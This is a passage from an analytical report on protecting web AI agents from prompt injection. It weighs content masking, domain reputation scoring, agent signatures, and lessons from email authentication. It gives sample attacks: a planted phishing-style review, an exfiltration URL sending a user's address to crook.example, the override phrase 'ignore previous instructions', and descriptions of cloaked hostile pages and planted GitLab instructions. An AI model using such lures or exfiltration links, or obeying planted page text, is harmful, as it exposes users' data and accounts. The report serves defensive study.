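An agent that reads llms.txt can go straight to the prices without working through menus and banners. The second version lets a page link to the file, so an agent doesn't have to guess where it is. The site specification.website recommends llms.txt to site owners but doesn't report how many sites have one or which AI companies read it. Whether the file is worth maintaining depends on which companies read it, because if no agent reads Ana's list, she has only created a second set of prices to keep up to date.

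An llms.txt file is already a declaration of "content intended for AI consumption", in the words of Franklin and colleagues. It doesn't make agents safer, because an attacker can publish one too, and few human visitors will open it and notice that something is wrong. Other text that people don't see has the same problem. OpenAI asks site owners to add ARIA tags, which describe buttons and other page elements and were originally meant for screen readers, so that its ChatGPT Atlas browser can use their pages more reliably. Franklin and colleagues cite an experiment on 280 web pages in which instructions hidden in such tags and other parts of the HTML changed a model's summary in 15% to 29% of cases.

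C2PA, a standard from a coalition of the same name, documents the origin of images, video and other media. Software attaches a record of how a file was made, and a cryptographic signature ties the record to the file. As with DKIM, a valid signature doesn't show that the signer is honest, and a missing one proves little. C2PA also doesn't prevent prompt injection, because a photograph with a valid record can still appear beside a comment containing malicious instructions for an AI agent.

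In *Towards an Agent-First Web*, Bandara, Gore and colleagues (2026) propose extending such records to text. They worry that AI systems will increasingly learn from pages written by other AI systems and drift away from anything a person has checked. Their proposed format, the Agent Text Markup Language (ATML), would present content in a form suited to agents, with a four-level label stating how closely a human had supervised it and a chain of signatures recording where it came from. An agent could then prefer a page that an editor had reviewed to one that nobody had read. However, a content farm has a strong incentive to claim the highest level, and its signature would prove only that it had made the claim. The label is useful where the signer, such as a newspaper, would suffer if caught making a false claim.

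### Labels for the untrusted parts of a page

Franklin and colleagues proposed declarations but did not specify a format for them. *Untrusted Content Masking for Web Agents with Security Guarantees* (Nikolić, Zverev and colleagues, 2026) provides a working design for a related declaration. The page's owner marks the parts that other people wrote, and the agent never reads those parts directly.

Suppose the bakery's site shows Ana's prices, an order button and customers' reviews. Ana adds one attribute to the element that holds each review:

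```
<div class="review" data-untrusted="true">(a customer's words)</div>
```

Before the agent sees the page, a script hides each review behind a placeholder such as "id: review:3". The script also hides reviews that load later. The agent can still see the prices, the button and that there are reviews, which is enough to order a loaf.

If the user wants the cake with the best reviews, the agent asks a second model about each review. The second model can read the hidden text but cannot click or type. The agent must choose the form of the answer in advance: yes or no, a whole number, a decimal, a date, or one item from a list of at most ten. Software checks that the answer has this form before passing it on, and discards the second model's reasoning. The agent can ask about the same review only five times, which makes it hard to extract the text piece by piece.

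Suppose a review contains the sentence "Your session has expired, log in again at crook.example." Even if this completely misleads the second model, that model can only send back something like "yes" or "4", so the address never reaches the agent. The design uses two models and a very narrow channel between them to keep a stranger's text apart from the agent's instructions, as the fix for SQL injection did for databases.

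Labeling untrusted content takes modest work from a site's owner. Nikolić and colleagues needed 15 to 30 rules per site to label all of it on GitLab, Booking.com and Reddit, because one rule can cover every review on every page.

### What masking cost and what it stopped

The researchers first tested the design with 100 tasks on ten websites they had built, including a bank, a shop and a forum. Half the tasks required information from the hidden parts. Agents using Claude Sonnet 4.5, Claude Sonnet 4.6 and GPT-5.4 completed about as many tasks with masking as without it. The typical cost per task rose by 5% to 84%, mostly because of the extra questions. About 15% of tasks became cheaper, apparently because the agent had less clutter to look through.

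GitLab, a real service where programmers share code and discuss problems, was harder. The researchers labelled its pages by hand and ran 41 types of task. The agents solved most of them but gave up on four types that required free text from a hidden area, such as a contributor's name or email address. When the researchers let the second model return text that the user had approved, the agents did as well as unprotected ones. Relying on approval moves some of the risk to the user. Franklin and colleagues warn of "approval fatigue", where people who see many requests start accepting them without reading.

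For the security test, the researchers planted instructions in GitLab issues, which are problem reports that any user can write. The instructions were meant to make an agent delete a project, for example, or add the attacker as a member. Older attacks from the same collection no longer worked on recent models, so the researchers strengthened them and chose a task that forced the agent to read the issue carefully. The agent ran on Claude Sonnet 4, a 2025 model.

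| Defence | Attacks that succeeded |
|---|---|
| None | 17% |
| A warning in the agent's instructions | 8% |
| Masking | 0% |
| Masking, with the attacked element wrongly labelled as trusted | 6% |

The test had only 12 attack goals, so 17% is about two successes, and the difference between 8% and 6% is not meaningful. The 0% result is stronger evidence than a test this small would normally provide, because the design keeps the planted text from reaching the agent. A single wrong label lets the text through, and the agent is then about as safe as it would be with only the warning.

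Attackers can still corrupt the second model's answers. Suppose a user asks an agent to invite a colleague to a project called "dotfiles". Project names are hidden from the agent, so it asks the second model "Is this project called dotfiles?" for each project in turn and stops at the first yes. An attacker who has planted a project near the top of the list, with a name that deceives the second model, can get the colleague invited to the wrong project. Nikolić and colleagues found this by simulating an attacker with full control over the second model's answers, which is more than a real attacker is likely to have. They suggest asking about all the candidates at once and treating two matches as a sign of tampering.

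Opinions are harder to corrupt when an agent adds them up. If the agent checks 50 reviews of Ana's cakes separately, a hostile instruction in one review can change only that review's answer, which is 2% of the total. Someone who posts 20 fake reviews can do far more damage, but they could mislead a human reader the same way.

### Labels that the agent's operator infers

Most site owners will not label anything soon, so Nikolić and colleagues tested whether a model could work out the labels. Giving the model the whole page would expose it to the text it was supposed to flag, so they removed all the wording and kept the structure. A title, for example, becomes something like "text, 79 characters". The model can still recognise a list of comments from names such as "post-content" in the HTML. They also gave it a short description of the site and examples of what would be untrusted there.

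On Reddit it found every type of untrusted element, but it missed about 7% of the types on Booking.com, where many names in the HTML are random strings, and about 10% on GitLab. Around a fifth of what it masked on GitLab was the site's own content. Hiding that content makes tasks slower or impossible but does not let an attacker in. The missed elements are the serious errors, because an attacker can look for an unlabeled place and write there.

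### When the site itself is hostile

Both versions assume that the site's owner is honest. Nikolić and colleagues defend this assumption by pointing out that a malicious page can do harm as soon as it loads, and that half of all web traffic goes to 3,000 domains, mostly run by established organisations. They suggest applying masking to a list of trusted sites and relying on weaker defences everywhere else.

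That leaves out most of the injections that Khodayari and colleagues found, since site operators had planted about four-fifths of them. Even if every honest owner had labeled their content perfectly, the labels would have covered only the rest. But counting pages doesn't show how many agents were affected. One hostile comment on a site with millions of visitors may reach more agents than a thousand malicious pages with few visitors, and an attacker who can post on GitLab has little need to build a website and attract agents to it.

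A declaration that asks for more trust is least useful where agents most need protection, because hostile sites benefit from adopting it. In a hypothetical group of 1,000 sites, 50 are hostile, and a standard tag means "this page is safe for AI agents". All 50 hostile sites adopt the tag at once, but only 300 of the honest ones do. About 14% of the tagged sites are then hostile, compared with 5% of all sites, so an agent that trusted the tag would be choosing the more dangerous group. Spammers similarly adopted SPF while most honest companies were still deciding whether to use it.

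An agent can usually believe an "untrusted" label whoever publishes it, even a fraudster, because the label only makes the agent more careful with the marked text. But masking the marked text can hide the truth. On a page like Saxton's, which listed a subscription at £52, a dishonest seller could label the price as untrusted and leave the word "free" unlabelled. The agent would see "free" and a placeholder, and might have no reason to ask what was behind it.

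The greater danger is a missing label. On a trusted site, masking treats everything unlabelled as the owner's own words. If an operator applied that rule everywhere, a hostile site could get its instructions treated the same way by leaving them unlabelled. Treating every page on an unfamiliar site as untrusted is safer, but it prevents the agent from doing even simple tasks such as summarising an article. An operator who wants to relax the stricter rule for some sites needs information from another source, such as a score for the domain.

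A refusal such as `ai-train=no` states the publisher's wish, and a hostile site gains nothing by pretending not to want its pages in a training set. Such refusals fail when a dishonest reader ignores them, whereas declarations meant to protect agents fail when the publisher lies.

### Who gains from publishing them

Publishers have reason to restrict AI crawlers, which take many pages and send back few visitors. Chowdhury reports Cloudflare's mid-2026 counts of pages fetched for each visitor referred: about five for Google, 190 for Perplexity, the high hundreds for OpenAI and just under 2,000 for Anthropic. The true figures are probably lower, because visits from phone apps often don't reveal where they came from, and Cloudflare sells tools to deal with the imbalance. Even if the counts are far off, a news site that depends on advertising does badly from the exchange. Adding a line to robots.txt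 takes almost no effort, so it is worth doing even if only a few large companies obey it.

Ana has different interests. She earns money from each cake sold, whether a person or an agent orders it, so she gains from llms.txt or ARIA tags if agents use them. She gains much less from labelling her reviews. If a hostile review diverts a customer's agent, the customer suffers and may blame the company that made the agent. Ana might lose a sale, but she would probably never find out why. Franklin and colleagues note that the law has not settled how to divide responsibility among the agent's operator, the model's maker and the domain's owner. If domain owners had to pay for some of the damage, they would see labels as a cheap precaution.

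A large marketplace or a service like GitLab has more to lose if customers decide agents aren't safe there, and its engineers could write 30 rules in an afternoon. Agent operators benefit most directly. They can also start without waiting for anyone else, by inferring labels for the sites their users visit most, just as a mail receiver in 1997 could start using a blocklist without asking senders to change anything.

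## Source reputation for AI agents, 2025 to 2026

To decide how much to trust each website, an agent operator needs evidence that doesn't come from the website itself. Franklin and colleagues proposed scoring domains on the open web, where nobody has vetted the content, by their record of hosting malicious material. They separately proposed source filters, a technical defence that would check the credibility of outside content before it enters the agent's context, the text that the model works from.

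The paper doesn't explicitly connect the two proposals, but they fit together because a filter needs a basis for its decisions and a score has no effect until a program acts on it. The paper also doesn't define "malicious."

### How a score could work

Suppose a customer asks an agent to order a birthday cake, and a web search returns ten sites, including Ana's. Before the agent opens any of them, a small program looks up each domain's score and removes those with a bad record from the results. If a domain has little or no record, the agent may read the site but can't enter card details there. The program has to be separate from the language model because text on a page can affect what the model does without changing the result of a lookup. It also has to check whenever the agent follows a link, since the next page may belong to a different domain.

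The most direct evidence for a score would come from scans, in which a program searches a site for instructions aimed at AI systems. Reports could reveal attacks that the scans missed. Gmail scored senders partly from its users' clicks on "Report Spam", but those users could see the spam. A person whose agent bought the wrong cake may never find out that a web page caused the mistake. Franklin and colleagues expect that even forensic investigators will struggle to trace an agent's output back to the page that influenced it.

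Some people would also abuse reports. Franklin and colleagues describe Sybil attacks, in which one person uses many false identities to distort a reputation system. One of Ana's competitors could post a hostile review on her site and then report the site under fifty names.

A domain's age and its server's history are useful because they are available before the first attack. *What It Is, Not What It Says* (Iqbal, 2026) describes a test in which researchers asked Comet, a browser with a built-in agent, to buy an Apple Watch from a fake Walmart store. In some runs, the agent filled in the saved address and card details and completed the purchase without asking. A fake shop like this usually has a new domain, so a rule against paying on new domains could prevent the loss even if nobody had reported the shop. But the rule would also stop agents from buying from legitimate new shops, such as a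 baker's first website, opened this week with the cheapest hosting company she could find.

### What browsers and agent operators already check

For years, browsers have used reputation services such as Microsoft's SmartScreen and Google's Safe Browsing to identify phishing and malware sites, which they then block or warn the user about. An agent inside the browser can use the same service. The Hacker News (2025) reports that Chrome's agent works alongside Safe Browsing, and that a classifier also checks each page for indirect prompt injections.

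The classifier examines the page the agent has open, so it doesn't depend on the domain's record. In Chrome, a separate program that never reads untrusted web content must also approve each new site before the agent can use it. According to SecurityWeek, the user must confirm before the agent opens a banking or medical site, makes a purchase or sends a message.

OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) explains why the company decided that a list of trusted sites wasn't enough to prevent one kind of data theft. An attacker's page can tell an agent to open a web address that contains private information, such as the user's street address:

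```
crook.example/collect?data=14-Mill-Lane
```

The request itself delivers the information, because web servers commonly log every address that visitors ask for. Restricting agents to well-known domains doesn't fully prevent this. Many legitimate sites redirect visitors elsewhere, so a link to a trusted domain can lead to crook.example. OpenAI also worried that a strict list would produce frequent warnings and teach people to click through them without thinking.

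OpenAI therefore checks whether the exact address is already public. A crawler with no access to users' conversations keeps an index of addresses it has found on the open web, and the agent can automatically open any address in that index. The address above is unlikely to be there because it contains one user's data, so the agent would have to try another site or show the user a warning. OpenAI uses the same mechanism for pages that its Atlas browser and Deep Research tool visit.

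This check protects the user's data but doesn't keep hostile text away from the agent. If crook.example has a public page about cakes with a hidden instruction, the page can be in the index, and the agent will open it. OpenAI acknowledges that a matching address doesn't make the content trustworthy.

OpenAI's advice to users still relies on reputation. In October 2025 its head of security, quoted by the software developer Simon Willison, recommended that people let the agent use their logged-in accounts mainly for well-defined tasks on "very trusted sites", where the risk of prompt injection was lower. Users have to decide which sites those are.

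### An objection from inside SmartScreen

Microsoft's SmartScreen blocks phishing, malware and technical-support scams. Eric Lawrence, who works on the service, writes in *AI Injection Attacks* (2025) that it should keep agents away from bad sites and already does, but that this is "wildly insufficient". The number of bad sites grows by the second, and Lawrence thought it very unlikely that anyone would recognise a site that was attacking agents with planted text.

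Lawrence also considers allowing only sites known to be good, but no list of such sites exists. The closest thing SmartScreen has is a list of high-traffic sites that are unlikely to be sources of the threats it covers, which don't include prompt injection. Many reputable sites carry comments, adverts and extracts from other websites, any of which could contain an injection.

The point about recognition has weakened since September 2025. By that December, Google had announced Chrome's injection classifier, and the security company Palo Alto Networks now says its web filters help protect customers from injections its researchers find. But better detection doesn't remove the problem of comments and adverts. In describing Chrome's defences, Google says injections can appear in user reviews and embedded third-party content.

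### What searches of the live web found

Someone has to find the injections before a domain can be scored on its past. Google and Khodayari et al. both searched Common Crawl, a public archive of web pages. Unit 42, the research arm of Palo Alto Networks, used the company's own monitoring data for *Fooling AI Agents*, published in March 2026.

| | Google | Unit 42 | Khodayari and colleagues |
|---|---|---|---|
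| Pages searched | Several versions of the archive, each with 2 to 3 billion pages | Company monitoring data, size not given | 1.2 billion addresses from October 2025 |
| Pages with injections | Not given | Not given | 9,676, on 285 hosts |
| Main kinds | Pranks, promotion and attempts to deter AI visitors | Irrelevant output 28.6%, data destruction 14.2%, getting past AI moderation 9.5% | Disrupting AI systems 58%, protecting data 27%, detecting bots 20% |
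| Domains | Not given | .com 73.2%, .dev 4.3%, .org 4.0% | Highest rates among sites ranked 100,000th to millionth |

A host is a single server name, such as shop.bakery.example. Khodayari and colleagues' percentages cover 15,387 injections, including some from two other search services, and one injection can have several purposes. Because .com is by far the most common domain ending, Unit 42's 73.2% doesn't show that .com is especially dangerous.

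Only the study by Khodayari and colleagues can show how common injections are. Unit 42 gives percentages without a total, and its data come from a company that looks for threats, so attacks probably make up a larger share than they would in a random sample. Both archive searches leave out most social media because Common Crawl doesn't collect it.

When Google searched for injections using phrases like "ignore previous instructions", most of the matches were harmless, and many came from research papers and articles about prompt injection. Google therefore used its Gemini model to classify the purpose of each match, and people then checked the results. Khodayari and colleagues found suspicious phrases on 999 hosts in the archive, but only 285 had a real injection. A reputation service that marked down every host with a match would have been wrong about 714 of them.

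Unit 42's own article could easily set off such a scanner because it discusses many malicious instructions and opens with a note for AI agents to treat them as educational and not follow them.

Even a real injection isn't always malicious. Unit 42 listed 16 sites and pages where it had found injections. One is a scam advert for "military glasses", with 24 attempts to make an AI moderator approve it. Unit 42 knows of no confirmed case in which such an attack worked on a moderation system in use. Another is an article about accessibility with hidden text that tells AI systems to print the word "cabbage" five million times, apparently to annoy scrapers. A reputation service would have to decide whether both deserve a bad score.

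The decision would affect most of the sites in the larger study. The most common injection there tells AI systems to ignore their instructions and return random numbers. Many others forbid the reuse of personal information or are meant to expose automated visitors. Only 13 of the 15,387 injections were attempts to extract secrets, and another 157 were commands meant to damage a system. More than half of the injections that site operators had placed in the archived pages were in HTTP headers, the technical lines sent with a page. Text extractors leave these out, so an agent that reads only the extracted text would never receive those injections.

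Some of the findings favour reputation scores. All 9,676 pages were on 285 of the 24.8 million hosts in the sample, so a short list would have covered them. Khodayari and colleagues also checked older copies of the pages in the Internet Archive and found that 66% of the copies from a year earlier already contained an injection. Even a slow reputation service could have listed those pages in time to warn later visitors, whereas spammers often abandon an address within minutes.

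Injections placed by criminals may not last this long. Somebody who wants to deter scrapers has no reason to take the text down, but a fraudster has good reason to move once a site gets a bad score. A single snapshot also over-represents long-lasting injections. An injection that stays up for one day of the year has a 1 in 365 chance of being online on the day of the snapshot, while one that stays up all year is certain to be.

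Unit 42's examples show how an attacker can benefit from the reputation of a trusted domain. Two of the listed addresses were under pages.dev, where Cloudflare hosts sites for many unrelated customers, so a bad score for the whole domain would have harmed all of them. Some of the listed sites used payment links at Stripe and PayPal, which an agent could hardly avoid visiting if it has to make payments.

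### Hostile text on familiar sites

Site operators had placed the injections on 179 of the 285 hosts. On another 25, the injections were in contributed material such as job adverts, and on 81 they were in comments and other user posts. On these 106 hosts, 37% of the total, a low score would have punished the domain for text its operator didn't write.

A site's popularity is only partly reassuring. Khodayari and colleagues found fewer injections among the 10,000 most popular sites, which supports OpenAI's advice about very trusted sites. But even among some popular sites, injection rates were higher for job listings, shopping, web hosting and phone companies than for other subjects. Agents are likely to visit shops and job boards often, because people want help buying things and finding work.

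A numerical score can't easily represent a site that publishes strangers' text. Suppose a job board has a million adverts and ten contain prompt injections. If the score is the percentage of clean pages, the board gets 99.999%. If one hostile page is enough to fail a site, the board fails, and eventually so will almost every large site of this kind. Neither result helps an agent decide whether the advert it is about to read is one of the ten.

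*It's a TRAP! Task-Redirecting Agent Persuasion Benchmark for Web Agents* tested attacks of this kind on copies of Amazon, Gmail, Google Calendar, LinkedIn, DoorDash and Upwork. The researchers planted text only where an outsider could plausibly write it. In one test, they put it in the location field of a calendar event. When the user asked about the event, the agent read the field and either finished the task or clicked a planted link to another website.

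The benchmark paired each of 18 tasks with 35 injections, and each of six models attempted all 630 combinations. The agents clicked in 948 of the 3,780 runs, or 25% on average. Buttons worked more than three times as often as links, and mentioning the user's task in the planted text raised the success rate by up to nearly six times. A click counted as a success for the attacker because the attacker controls everything the agent reads on the next site.

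The 25% shows that a good domain score is a poor guide to the text on a page. It doesn't measure how often an agent would encounter an injection on the real Amazon, because every run contained one. A score could still help when the agent clicks a link. All the planted links led to the same pornographic site, which an ordinary web filter would probably have blocked, but a real attacker could use a new domain with no record.

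Adverts and embedded services also add material from other companies to a page. Iqbal cites measurements showing that 92% of web pages include content or code from such third parties, and that the median site among the thousand most popular includes 66 of them. An operator could score each company separately, but would need to know which company wrote which part of the page.

Browsers don't reliably record who supplied each part of a page. If an advertising company's script writes a sentence into a site's page, the browser treats the sentence as the site's own. Iqbal found that, on 1,270 real pages, the browser attributed 58.7% of third-party elements to the site itself. Chrome's agent hides embedded frames that come from sites unrelated to its task, but this doesn't remove text that a script has written into the main page.

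Iqbal built a tool that records which script created or changed each element of a web page. In principle, an operator could use it to lower an advertising company's reputation without lowering that of every newspaper that carries its adverts. It wouldn't separate customer reviews from the rest of Ana's site, because Ana's server sends both and the tool treats everything the site's server sends as trusted.

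### Sites that show scanners a clean page

Cloaking undermines domain scores because a scanner can only check the page it receives. If crook.example sends scanners a harmless recipe and adds hidden instructions only for agents, the domain keeps its good score.

Franklin and colleagues cite work by Zychlinski that explains how a site can do this. A script checks the visitor's browser settings, network address and behaviour, and looks for traces of automation software. If the visitor appears to be an AI agent, the server returns a page that looks the same to a person but contains extra instructions, for example to misuse the agent's tools.

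If a site sends its hostile version to a random 5% of visitors, a scanner that visits ten times has a 40% chance of receiving it at least once (1 − 0.95¹⁰). Repeated scans don't help if the site recognises the scanner and always sends it the clean version.

Some attackers use simpler ways to avoid detection. In the scam advert that Unit 42 found, a script assembled some of the hidden instructions after a delay, so a scanner that read only the original page or finished too early would miss them.

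No one knows how many sites cloak against agents. Khodayari and colleagues note that a crawl can't detect a site that shows its injections only to particular agents. When they revisited pages with an automated browser in January 2026, about 34% of the injections in visible or hidden page elements were missing. Cloaking could have explained this, so they also checked the pages by hand in a normal browser. That would reveal an injection hidden from automated browsers, but not one shown only to a certain company's agent.

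Franklin and colleagues point out that cloaking would become easier if agents had to disclose their identity. But publishers have good reasons to want that disclosure, since they can't apply different rules to search engines, training crawlers and customers' agents without knowing which is which. Ana could use an agent's name to let in a customer's agent, and crook.example could use the same name to decide when to send its hostile page.

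A scanner could pretend to be an agent by using the agent's name and software. This becomes harder if agents sign their requests, as Chowdhury proposed for crawlers, because a security company can't produce a valid signature without the operator's key. The operator could run the scans itself, but a site might still notice that the scanner doesn't behave like an agent with a task.

Checking the copy the agent received, as Chrome's classifier does, avoids much of this problem. If an operator also added each detection to the domain's score, catching an attack on one user's agent could protect other users' agents. An operator with millions of users would learn about hostile sites much sooner than one with a few hundred.

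### Why most warnings would be false

Hostile pages are rare, so even a fairly accurate filter would mostly flag harmless ones. Suppose 1 page in 10,000 is hostile, and a filter catches 90% of the hostile pages but also wrongly flags 1% of the harmless ones. In a million pages, the results would be:

| | Hostile | Harmless | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Flagged | 90 | 9,999 | 10,089 |
| Not flagged | 10 | 989,901 | 989,911 |
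| Total | 100 | 999,900 | 1,000,000 |

Of the 10,089 flagged pages, 90 are hostile, or about 0.9%. For half of the flagged pages to be hostile, the filter would have to wrongly flag only about 1 in 11,000 harmless pages, instead of 1 in 100.

The problem is worse at the rate Khodayari and colleagues measured, about 1 page in 124,000. At that rate, the same filter would flag nearly 1,400 harmless pages for every page with an injection. But their count is a minimum, and agents don't choose pages at random, so agents could encounter injections more often.

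The filter in the example is still useful. About 1 in 99,000 of the pages it doesn't flag is hostile, so an agent that avoids flagged pages encounters only a tenth as many hostile ones. The harm from a false alarm depends on the task. An agent researching the history of bread can skip a flagged page and read another. But if the user wants a cake from Ana and the filter wrongly flags her page, she loses the order and may never learn why.

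An operator could instead let the agent read flagged pages but require the user's approval before it pays or sends anything. After a false alarm, the user would have to answer a question but could still get the cake. But if an agent opens 50 harmless pages during a task and the filter's mistakes are independent, the filter has a 39% chance of flagging at least one of them. Unnecessary questions in about two out of five such tasks would probably lead to approval fatigue.

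A domain score can make the filter's warnings more informative. Suppose 1 page in 500 is hostile on new domains and 1 in 100,000 on long-established ones. The filter's warnings would be right about 15% of the time on new domains and about 0.09% of the time on established ones. An operator could therefore block flagged pages on new domains and let agents read most flagged pages on established ones. But an attacker who knew this could post the injection as a comment on an established site.

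## How far the comparison with email holds

Two papers from the summer of 2026 use email's history to forecast what will happen to AI agents. Bandara and colleagues, who proposed supervision labels for text, also want agents to identify themselves to the sites they visit. An agent would give its name, the party it represents and its purpose, and its operator would sign the statement much as a mail server signs a message with DKIM. They expect dishonest agents to adapt, because SPF, DKIM and DMARC "shifted the attack surface rather than eliminating it". They predict that signatures will stop casual impostors and push skilled ones towards methods that take more resources.

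This account of email cites only the DKIM standard of 2007, which predates DMARC and so can't show how attackers responded to DMARC. The evidence from email supports only part of the claim, since nobody has measured whether blocked forgers switched to other methods or paid more for them.

The prediction is also about websites that must decide whether to trust an agent, which may be a scraper lying to get in. Franklin and colleagues' proposals deal with the reverse case, in which an agent must decide whether to trust a website. A fraudulent website lets everyone in and lies about what it offers.

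Gamba and colleagues ask who will control agents, using email spam filtering, ad blockers, recommendation systems and automated financial advice as precedents. They see the email industry's closed decision-making repeated in the Agentic AI Foundation, which oversees the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard for connecting agents to tools and data. Platform companies sit on the foundation's governing board, while user organisations have no formal standing.

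This argument is about power and doesn't depend on web pages resembling email. But MCP's history shows that a standard for agents can spread quickly. Anthropic released it in late 2024, and the major providers adopted it within a year. An agent that supports MCP can use more tools straight away, whereas a domain owner who published an SPF record in 2004 had to wait for receivers to check it.

### Web Bot Auth, for sites that want to identify agents

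Web Bot Auth is the main standard for identifying agents to websites. *HTTP Message Signatures for automated traffic* (Meunier and Major, 2026) sets out the current draft. Meunier works for Cloudflare and Major for Google.

Suppose an agent from helper.example visits Ana's online shop. Its operator keeps a private key and publishes the matching public key at a fixed location on helper.example. The agent adds three lines to each request, shown here without most of their details:

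```
Signature-Agent: helper.example
Signature-Input: (the parts signed, the key's name, the expiry time)
Signature: (the signature)
```

Ana's server, or a company such as Cloudflare that handles traffic for it, fetches the key from helper.example and checks the signature. It can keep the key for later visits. If the signature is valid, somebody who holds helper.example's key signed the request, and Ana can admit, limit or block helper.example by name.

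Anyone who copies a signed request can resend it until the signature expires. If the signature covers only the name of Ana's site, they can also attach it to a request for a different page there. *Explaining Web Bot Auth* (Rijo, 2026) reports that the draft recommends a signature lifetime of no more than 24 hours, while Cloudflare suggests about a minute.

Much of this is familiar from email. Meunier and Major want to replace IP addresses as identifiers because cloud customers share them and buyers may inherit an address's bad reputation. Both problems also affected mail blocklists. An intermediary that rewrites a signed line breaks the signature, as a mailing list does with DKIM. A valid signature also doesn't show "whether the Agent is benign", and an operator with a bad reputation can start again under another name. Meunier and Major don't try to prevent this, because they designed the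 protocol for honest operators that want sites to recognise them. They also leave out any way for sites to share assessments of agents, so Web Bot Auth has no blocklist of its own.

Companies began signing their agents' requests well before the standard was ready. Cloudflare published the idea in May 2025 and was accepting signatures by July. The IETF chartered a working group that October, but the group didn't adopt a draft until 1 September 2026. According to Rijo, OpenAI's ChatGPT agent and Amazon's AgentCore browser sign their requests. Google signs only some of its agent's requests, calls this an experiment, and advises sites to keep checking IP addresses.

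At the group's meeting in Montréal that November, three participants objected to the drafts and wanted to define the problem first (IETF, 2025). One of them, Eric Rescorla, has since co-written an alternative, *Anonymous Bot Authentication* (Rescorla and Barnes, 2026). It would let a site separate wanted from unwanted bots, and limit how often they visit, without tying a request to a particular sender. The email standards SPF, DKIM and DMARC didn't offer this, because they all work by naming a domain.

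A signature also identifies only the agent. Cloudflare's *Agents aren’t humans (but they kinda are)* (2026) points out that a site can't see which person is behind it. If one customer of helper.example places fake cake orders, blocking the agent would also turn away all its other customers, just as blocklisting a shared IP address blocks everyone who uses it. *Websites pay for nearly all 14 AI agent problems, Cloudflare argues* (Rijo, 2026) describes a proposed remedy, a "Hashed User ID" that would let Ana act against a single account.

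### Who does the work and who gains

Cloudflare's complaint, in Rijo's account, is that websites bear nearly all the costs of 14 problems that agents cause. Cloudflare sells websites protection from bots, so it has an interest in this view. But the costs do fall on different parties depending on the protection:

| Protection | Who does the work | Who gains most |
|---|---|---|
| Mail blocklist | List operator and receiver | Receiver and its users |
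| SPF, DKIM and DMARC | Domain owner and receiver | Receiver's users, and owners whose names criminals forge |
| Web Bot Auth | Agent operator and website | Website, and operators that want admission |
| Source reputation | Whoever keeps the scores, and agent operator | Agent's users |
| Labels for untrusted text | Website and agent operator | Agent's users |

A reputation score for websites has more in common with a 1997 email blocklist than with DMARC, because an agent operator can start using such a score today and its customers benefit even if no website cooperates. We can therefore infer little from the slow adoption of SPF and DMARC about how fast operators would adopt scores.

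Labels are closer to SPF, because the website has to act before the agent can. Ana would gain less from labelling a customer's review than a bank gained from publishing a DMARC policy, because the label mainly protects other people's agents, while the policy protected the bank's own name. But mistakes would probably do her less harm. Domain owners stayed at a DMARC policy of "none" because a stricter one could make genuine mail disappear. If Ana wrongly labels part of her page as untrusted, an agent may miss her opening hours or give up on an order, but her human customers still see the same page.

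### A few agent operators and many websites

In the early years of blocklists, thousands of organisations ran their own mail servers, and each had to decide which lists to use. But a few companies run the most popular AI agents, and each can protect all its users by adding a filter in a single update, without an industry standard.

Email reached a similar concentration only after decades, and the 2024 sender rules relied on it. In this respect, agents today are more like email in 2024 than in 1997. But agent operators may have less power over websites than Gmail has over bulk senders, because some websites don't want agents to visit.

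In the earlier model of adoption, an operator that refuses to read unlabelled websites puts pressure only on sites that benefit from agent visits. Suppose labelling costs a site 3, and the operator accounts for 40% of agent visits. A shop that values all its agent visits at 10 would lose 4 if the operator refused to read it, which is more than the cost of labelling, so it adds the labels. A newspaper that earns nothing from agents would lose nothing, so it can ignore the threat. It may even welcome the refusal, while the operator's users lose access to its news.

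Some agents would also fall outside the big companies' protection. Frameworks such as Browser Use let programmers build their own agents, and Saxton ran several at home. The owners of such agents would benefit from a reputation score only if somebody published it, and Google did not publish its scores for mail senders.

### Mail arrives, but an agent goes looking

A spammer can send a message to anyone whose address they have, and the recipient's mail server has to handle it. A hostile web page only reaches agents that visit it. Its author can try to attract them by getting the page ranked high in search results, planting links, or posting on a site that agents already use, but can't send the page to a million agents at once.

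The agent also has alternatives that a mail server lacks. If a search finds ten bakeries and one looks suspicious, the agent can order from another, and the user loses little if the suspicion was wrong. Someone expecting an email can't get the same message from a different sender. An agent operator can therefore accept more false alarms than a mail provider, at least for tasks that many websites could fulfill. This advantage disappears if the user wants a particular page. Even when the user can easily go elsewhere, a wrongly rejected bakery still loses the order.

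Ad blocking may be a better precedent than email, because it didn't require websites to cooperate, and many would have refused. An ad blocker checks each request against a list before the browser sends it, and cancels requests to known advertising domains. Volunteers maintain the best-known list, EasyList. Gamba and colleagues cite an estimate that one program, Adblock Plus, had about 100 million users by the late 2010s.

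The ad-blocking lists had problems that a reputation service for agents could share. Research cited by Gamba and colleagues found that ordinary browsing never triggered about 90% of EasyList's blocking rules, and that wrong entries could stay on the list for weeks or months. The publishers of roughly 6% to 7% of high-traffic sites fought back with scripts that detected ad blockers. Google later limited what extensions in its Chrome browser could block. People who use a company's agent would likewise need the company's permission to add a list of their own.

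Volunteers had the advantage that anyone can see an advert, whereas an instruction hidden in white text is much harder for the public to notice and report.

The difference between email and the web also disappears when an agent reads its user's inbox, because a stranger can then send text directly to the agent. The mail provider's spam filter then helps protect the agent.

### A known domain with unknown authors

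An agent can already use the certificate behind an "https" address to identify the domain a page came from. According to *Web Traffic Statistics Q3 2026* (2026), which uses Cloudflare's data, HTTPS accounted for 95.1% of web requests in the third quarter of 2026, up from 94.0% a year earlier. The figure covers only Cloudflare's traffic and counts requests rather than websites, but it is far above any measure of DMARC enforcement.

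SPF, DKIM and DMARC took about twenty years to provide what agents mostly have from the start, which is a way to verify the domain they are dealing with. Gmail had to work out which domain had sent each message before it could score senders, and it couldn't do so for all of them. A website's certificate lets an agent confirm which domain it has reached, so an operator can score bakery.example without first persuading Ana to publish anything. The certificate doesn't show that Ana is honest, and a fraudster can get one for a lookalike domain, just as phishers authenticate their own domains.

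Email is a poorer guide to what happens inside the page. One person usually writes an email, and a DKIM signature normally covers the whole text. A page in Ana's shop may combine her prices, a customer's review and an advert chosen a moment ago by a company she has never dealt with. Iqbal cites research finding that about half of websites show content loaded by an outside company. Ana can't label everything on her page because she doesn't always know what is there.

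The nearest parallel in email is a provider whose customers share a mail server. One hacked account can harm the reputation of all the others, and receivers rely on the provider to prevent this. But each message comes from one account, so a receiver can refuse it and accept the next. An agent would need to reject one paragraph on a web page and still read the price above it, which is a problem none of the email standards had to solve.

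### Three other standards, and one that stalled

The slow adoption of email authentication might have more to do with the peculiarities of email than with how protections generally spread. The adoption of HTTPS, authenticated caller ID and ads.txt provides a check on this.

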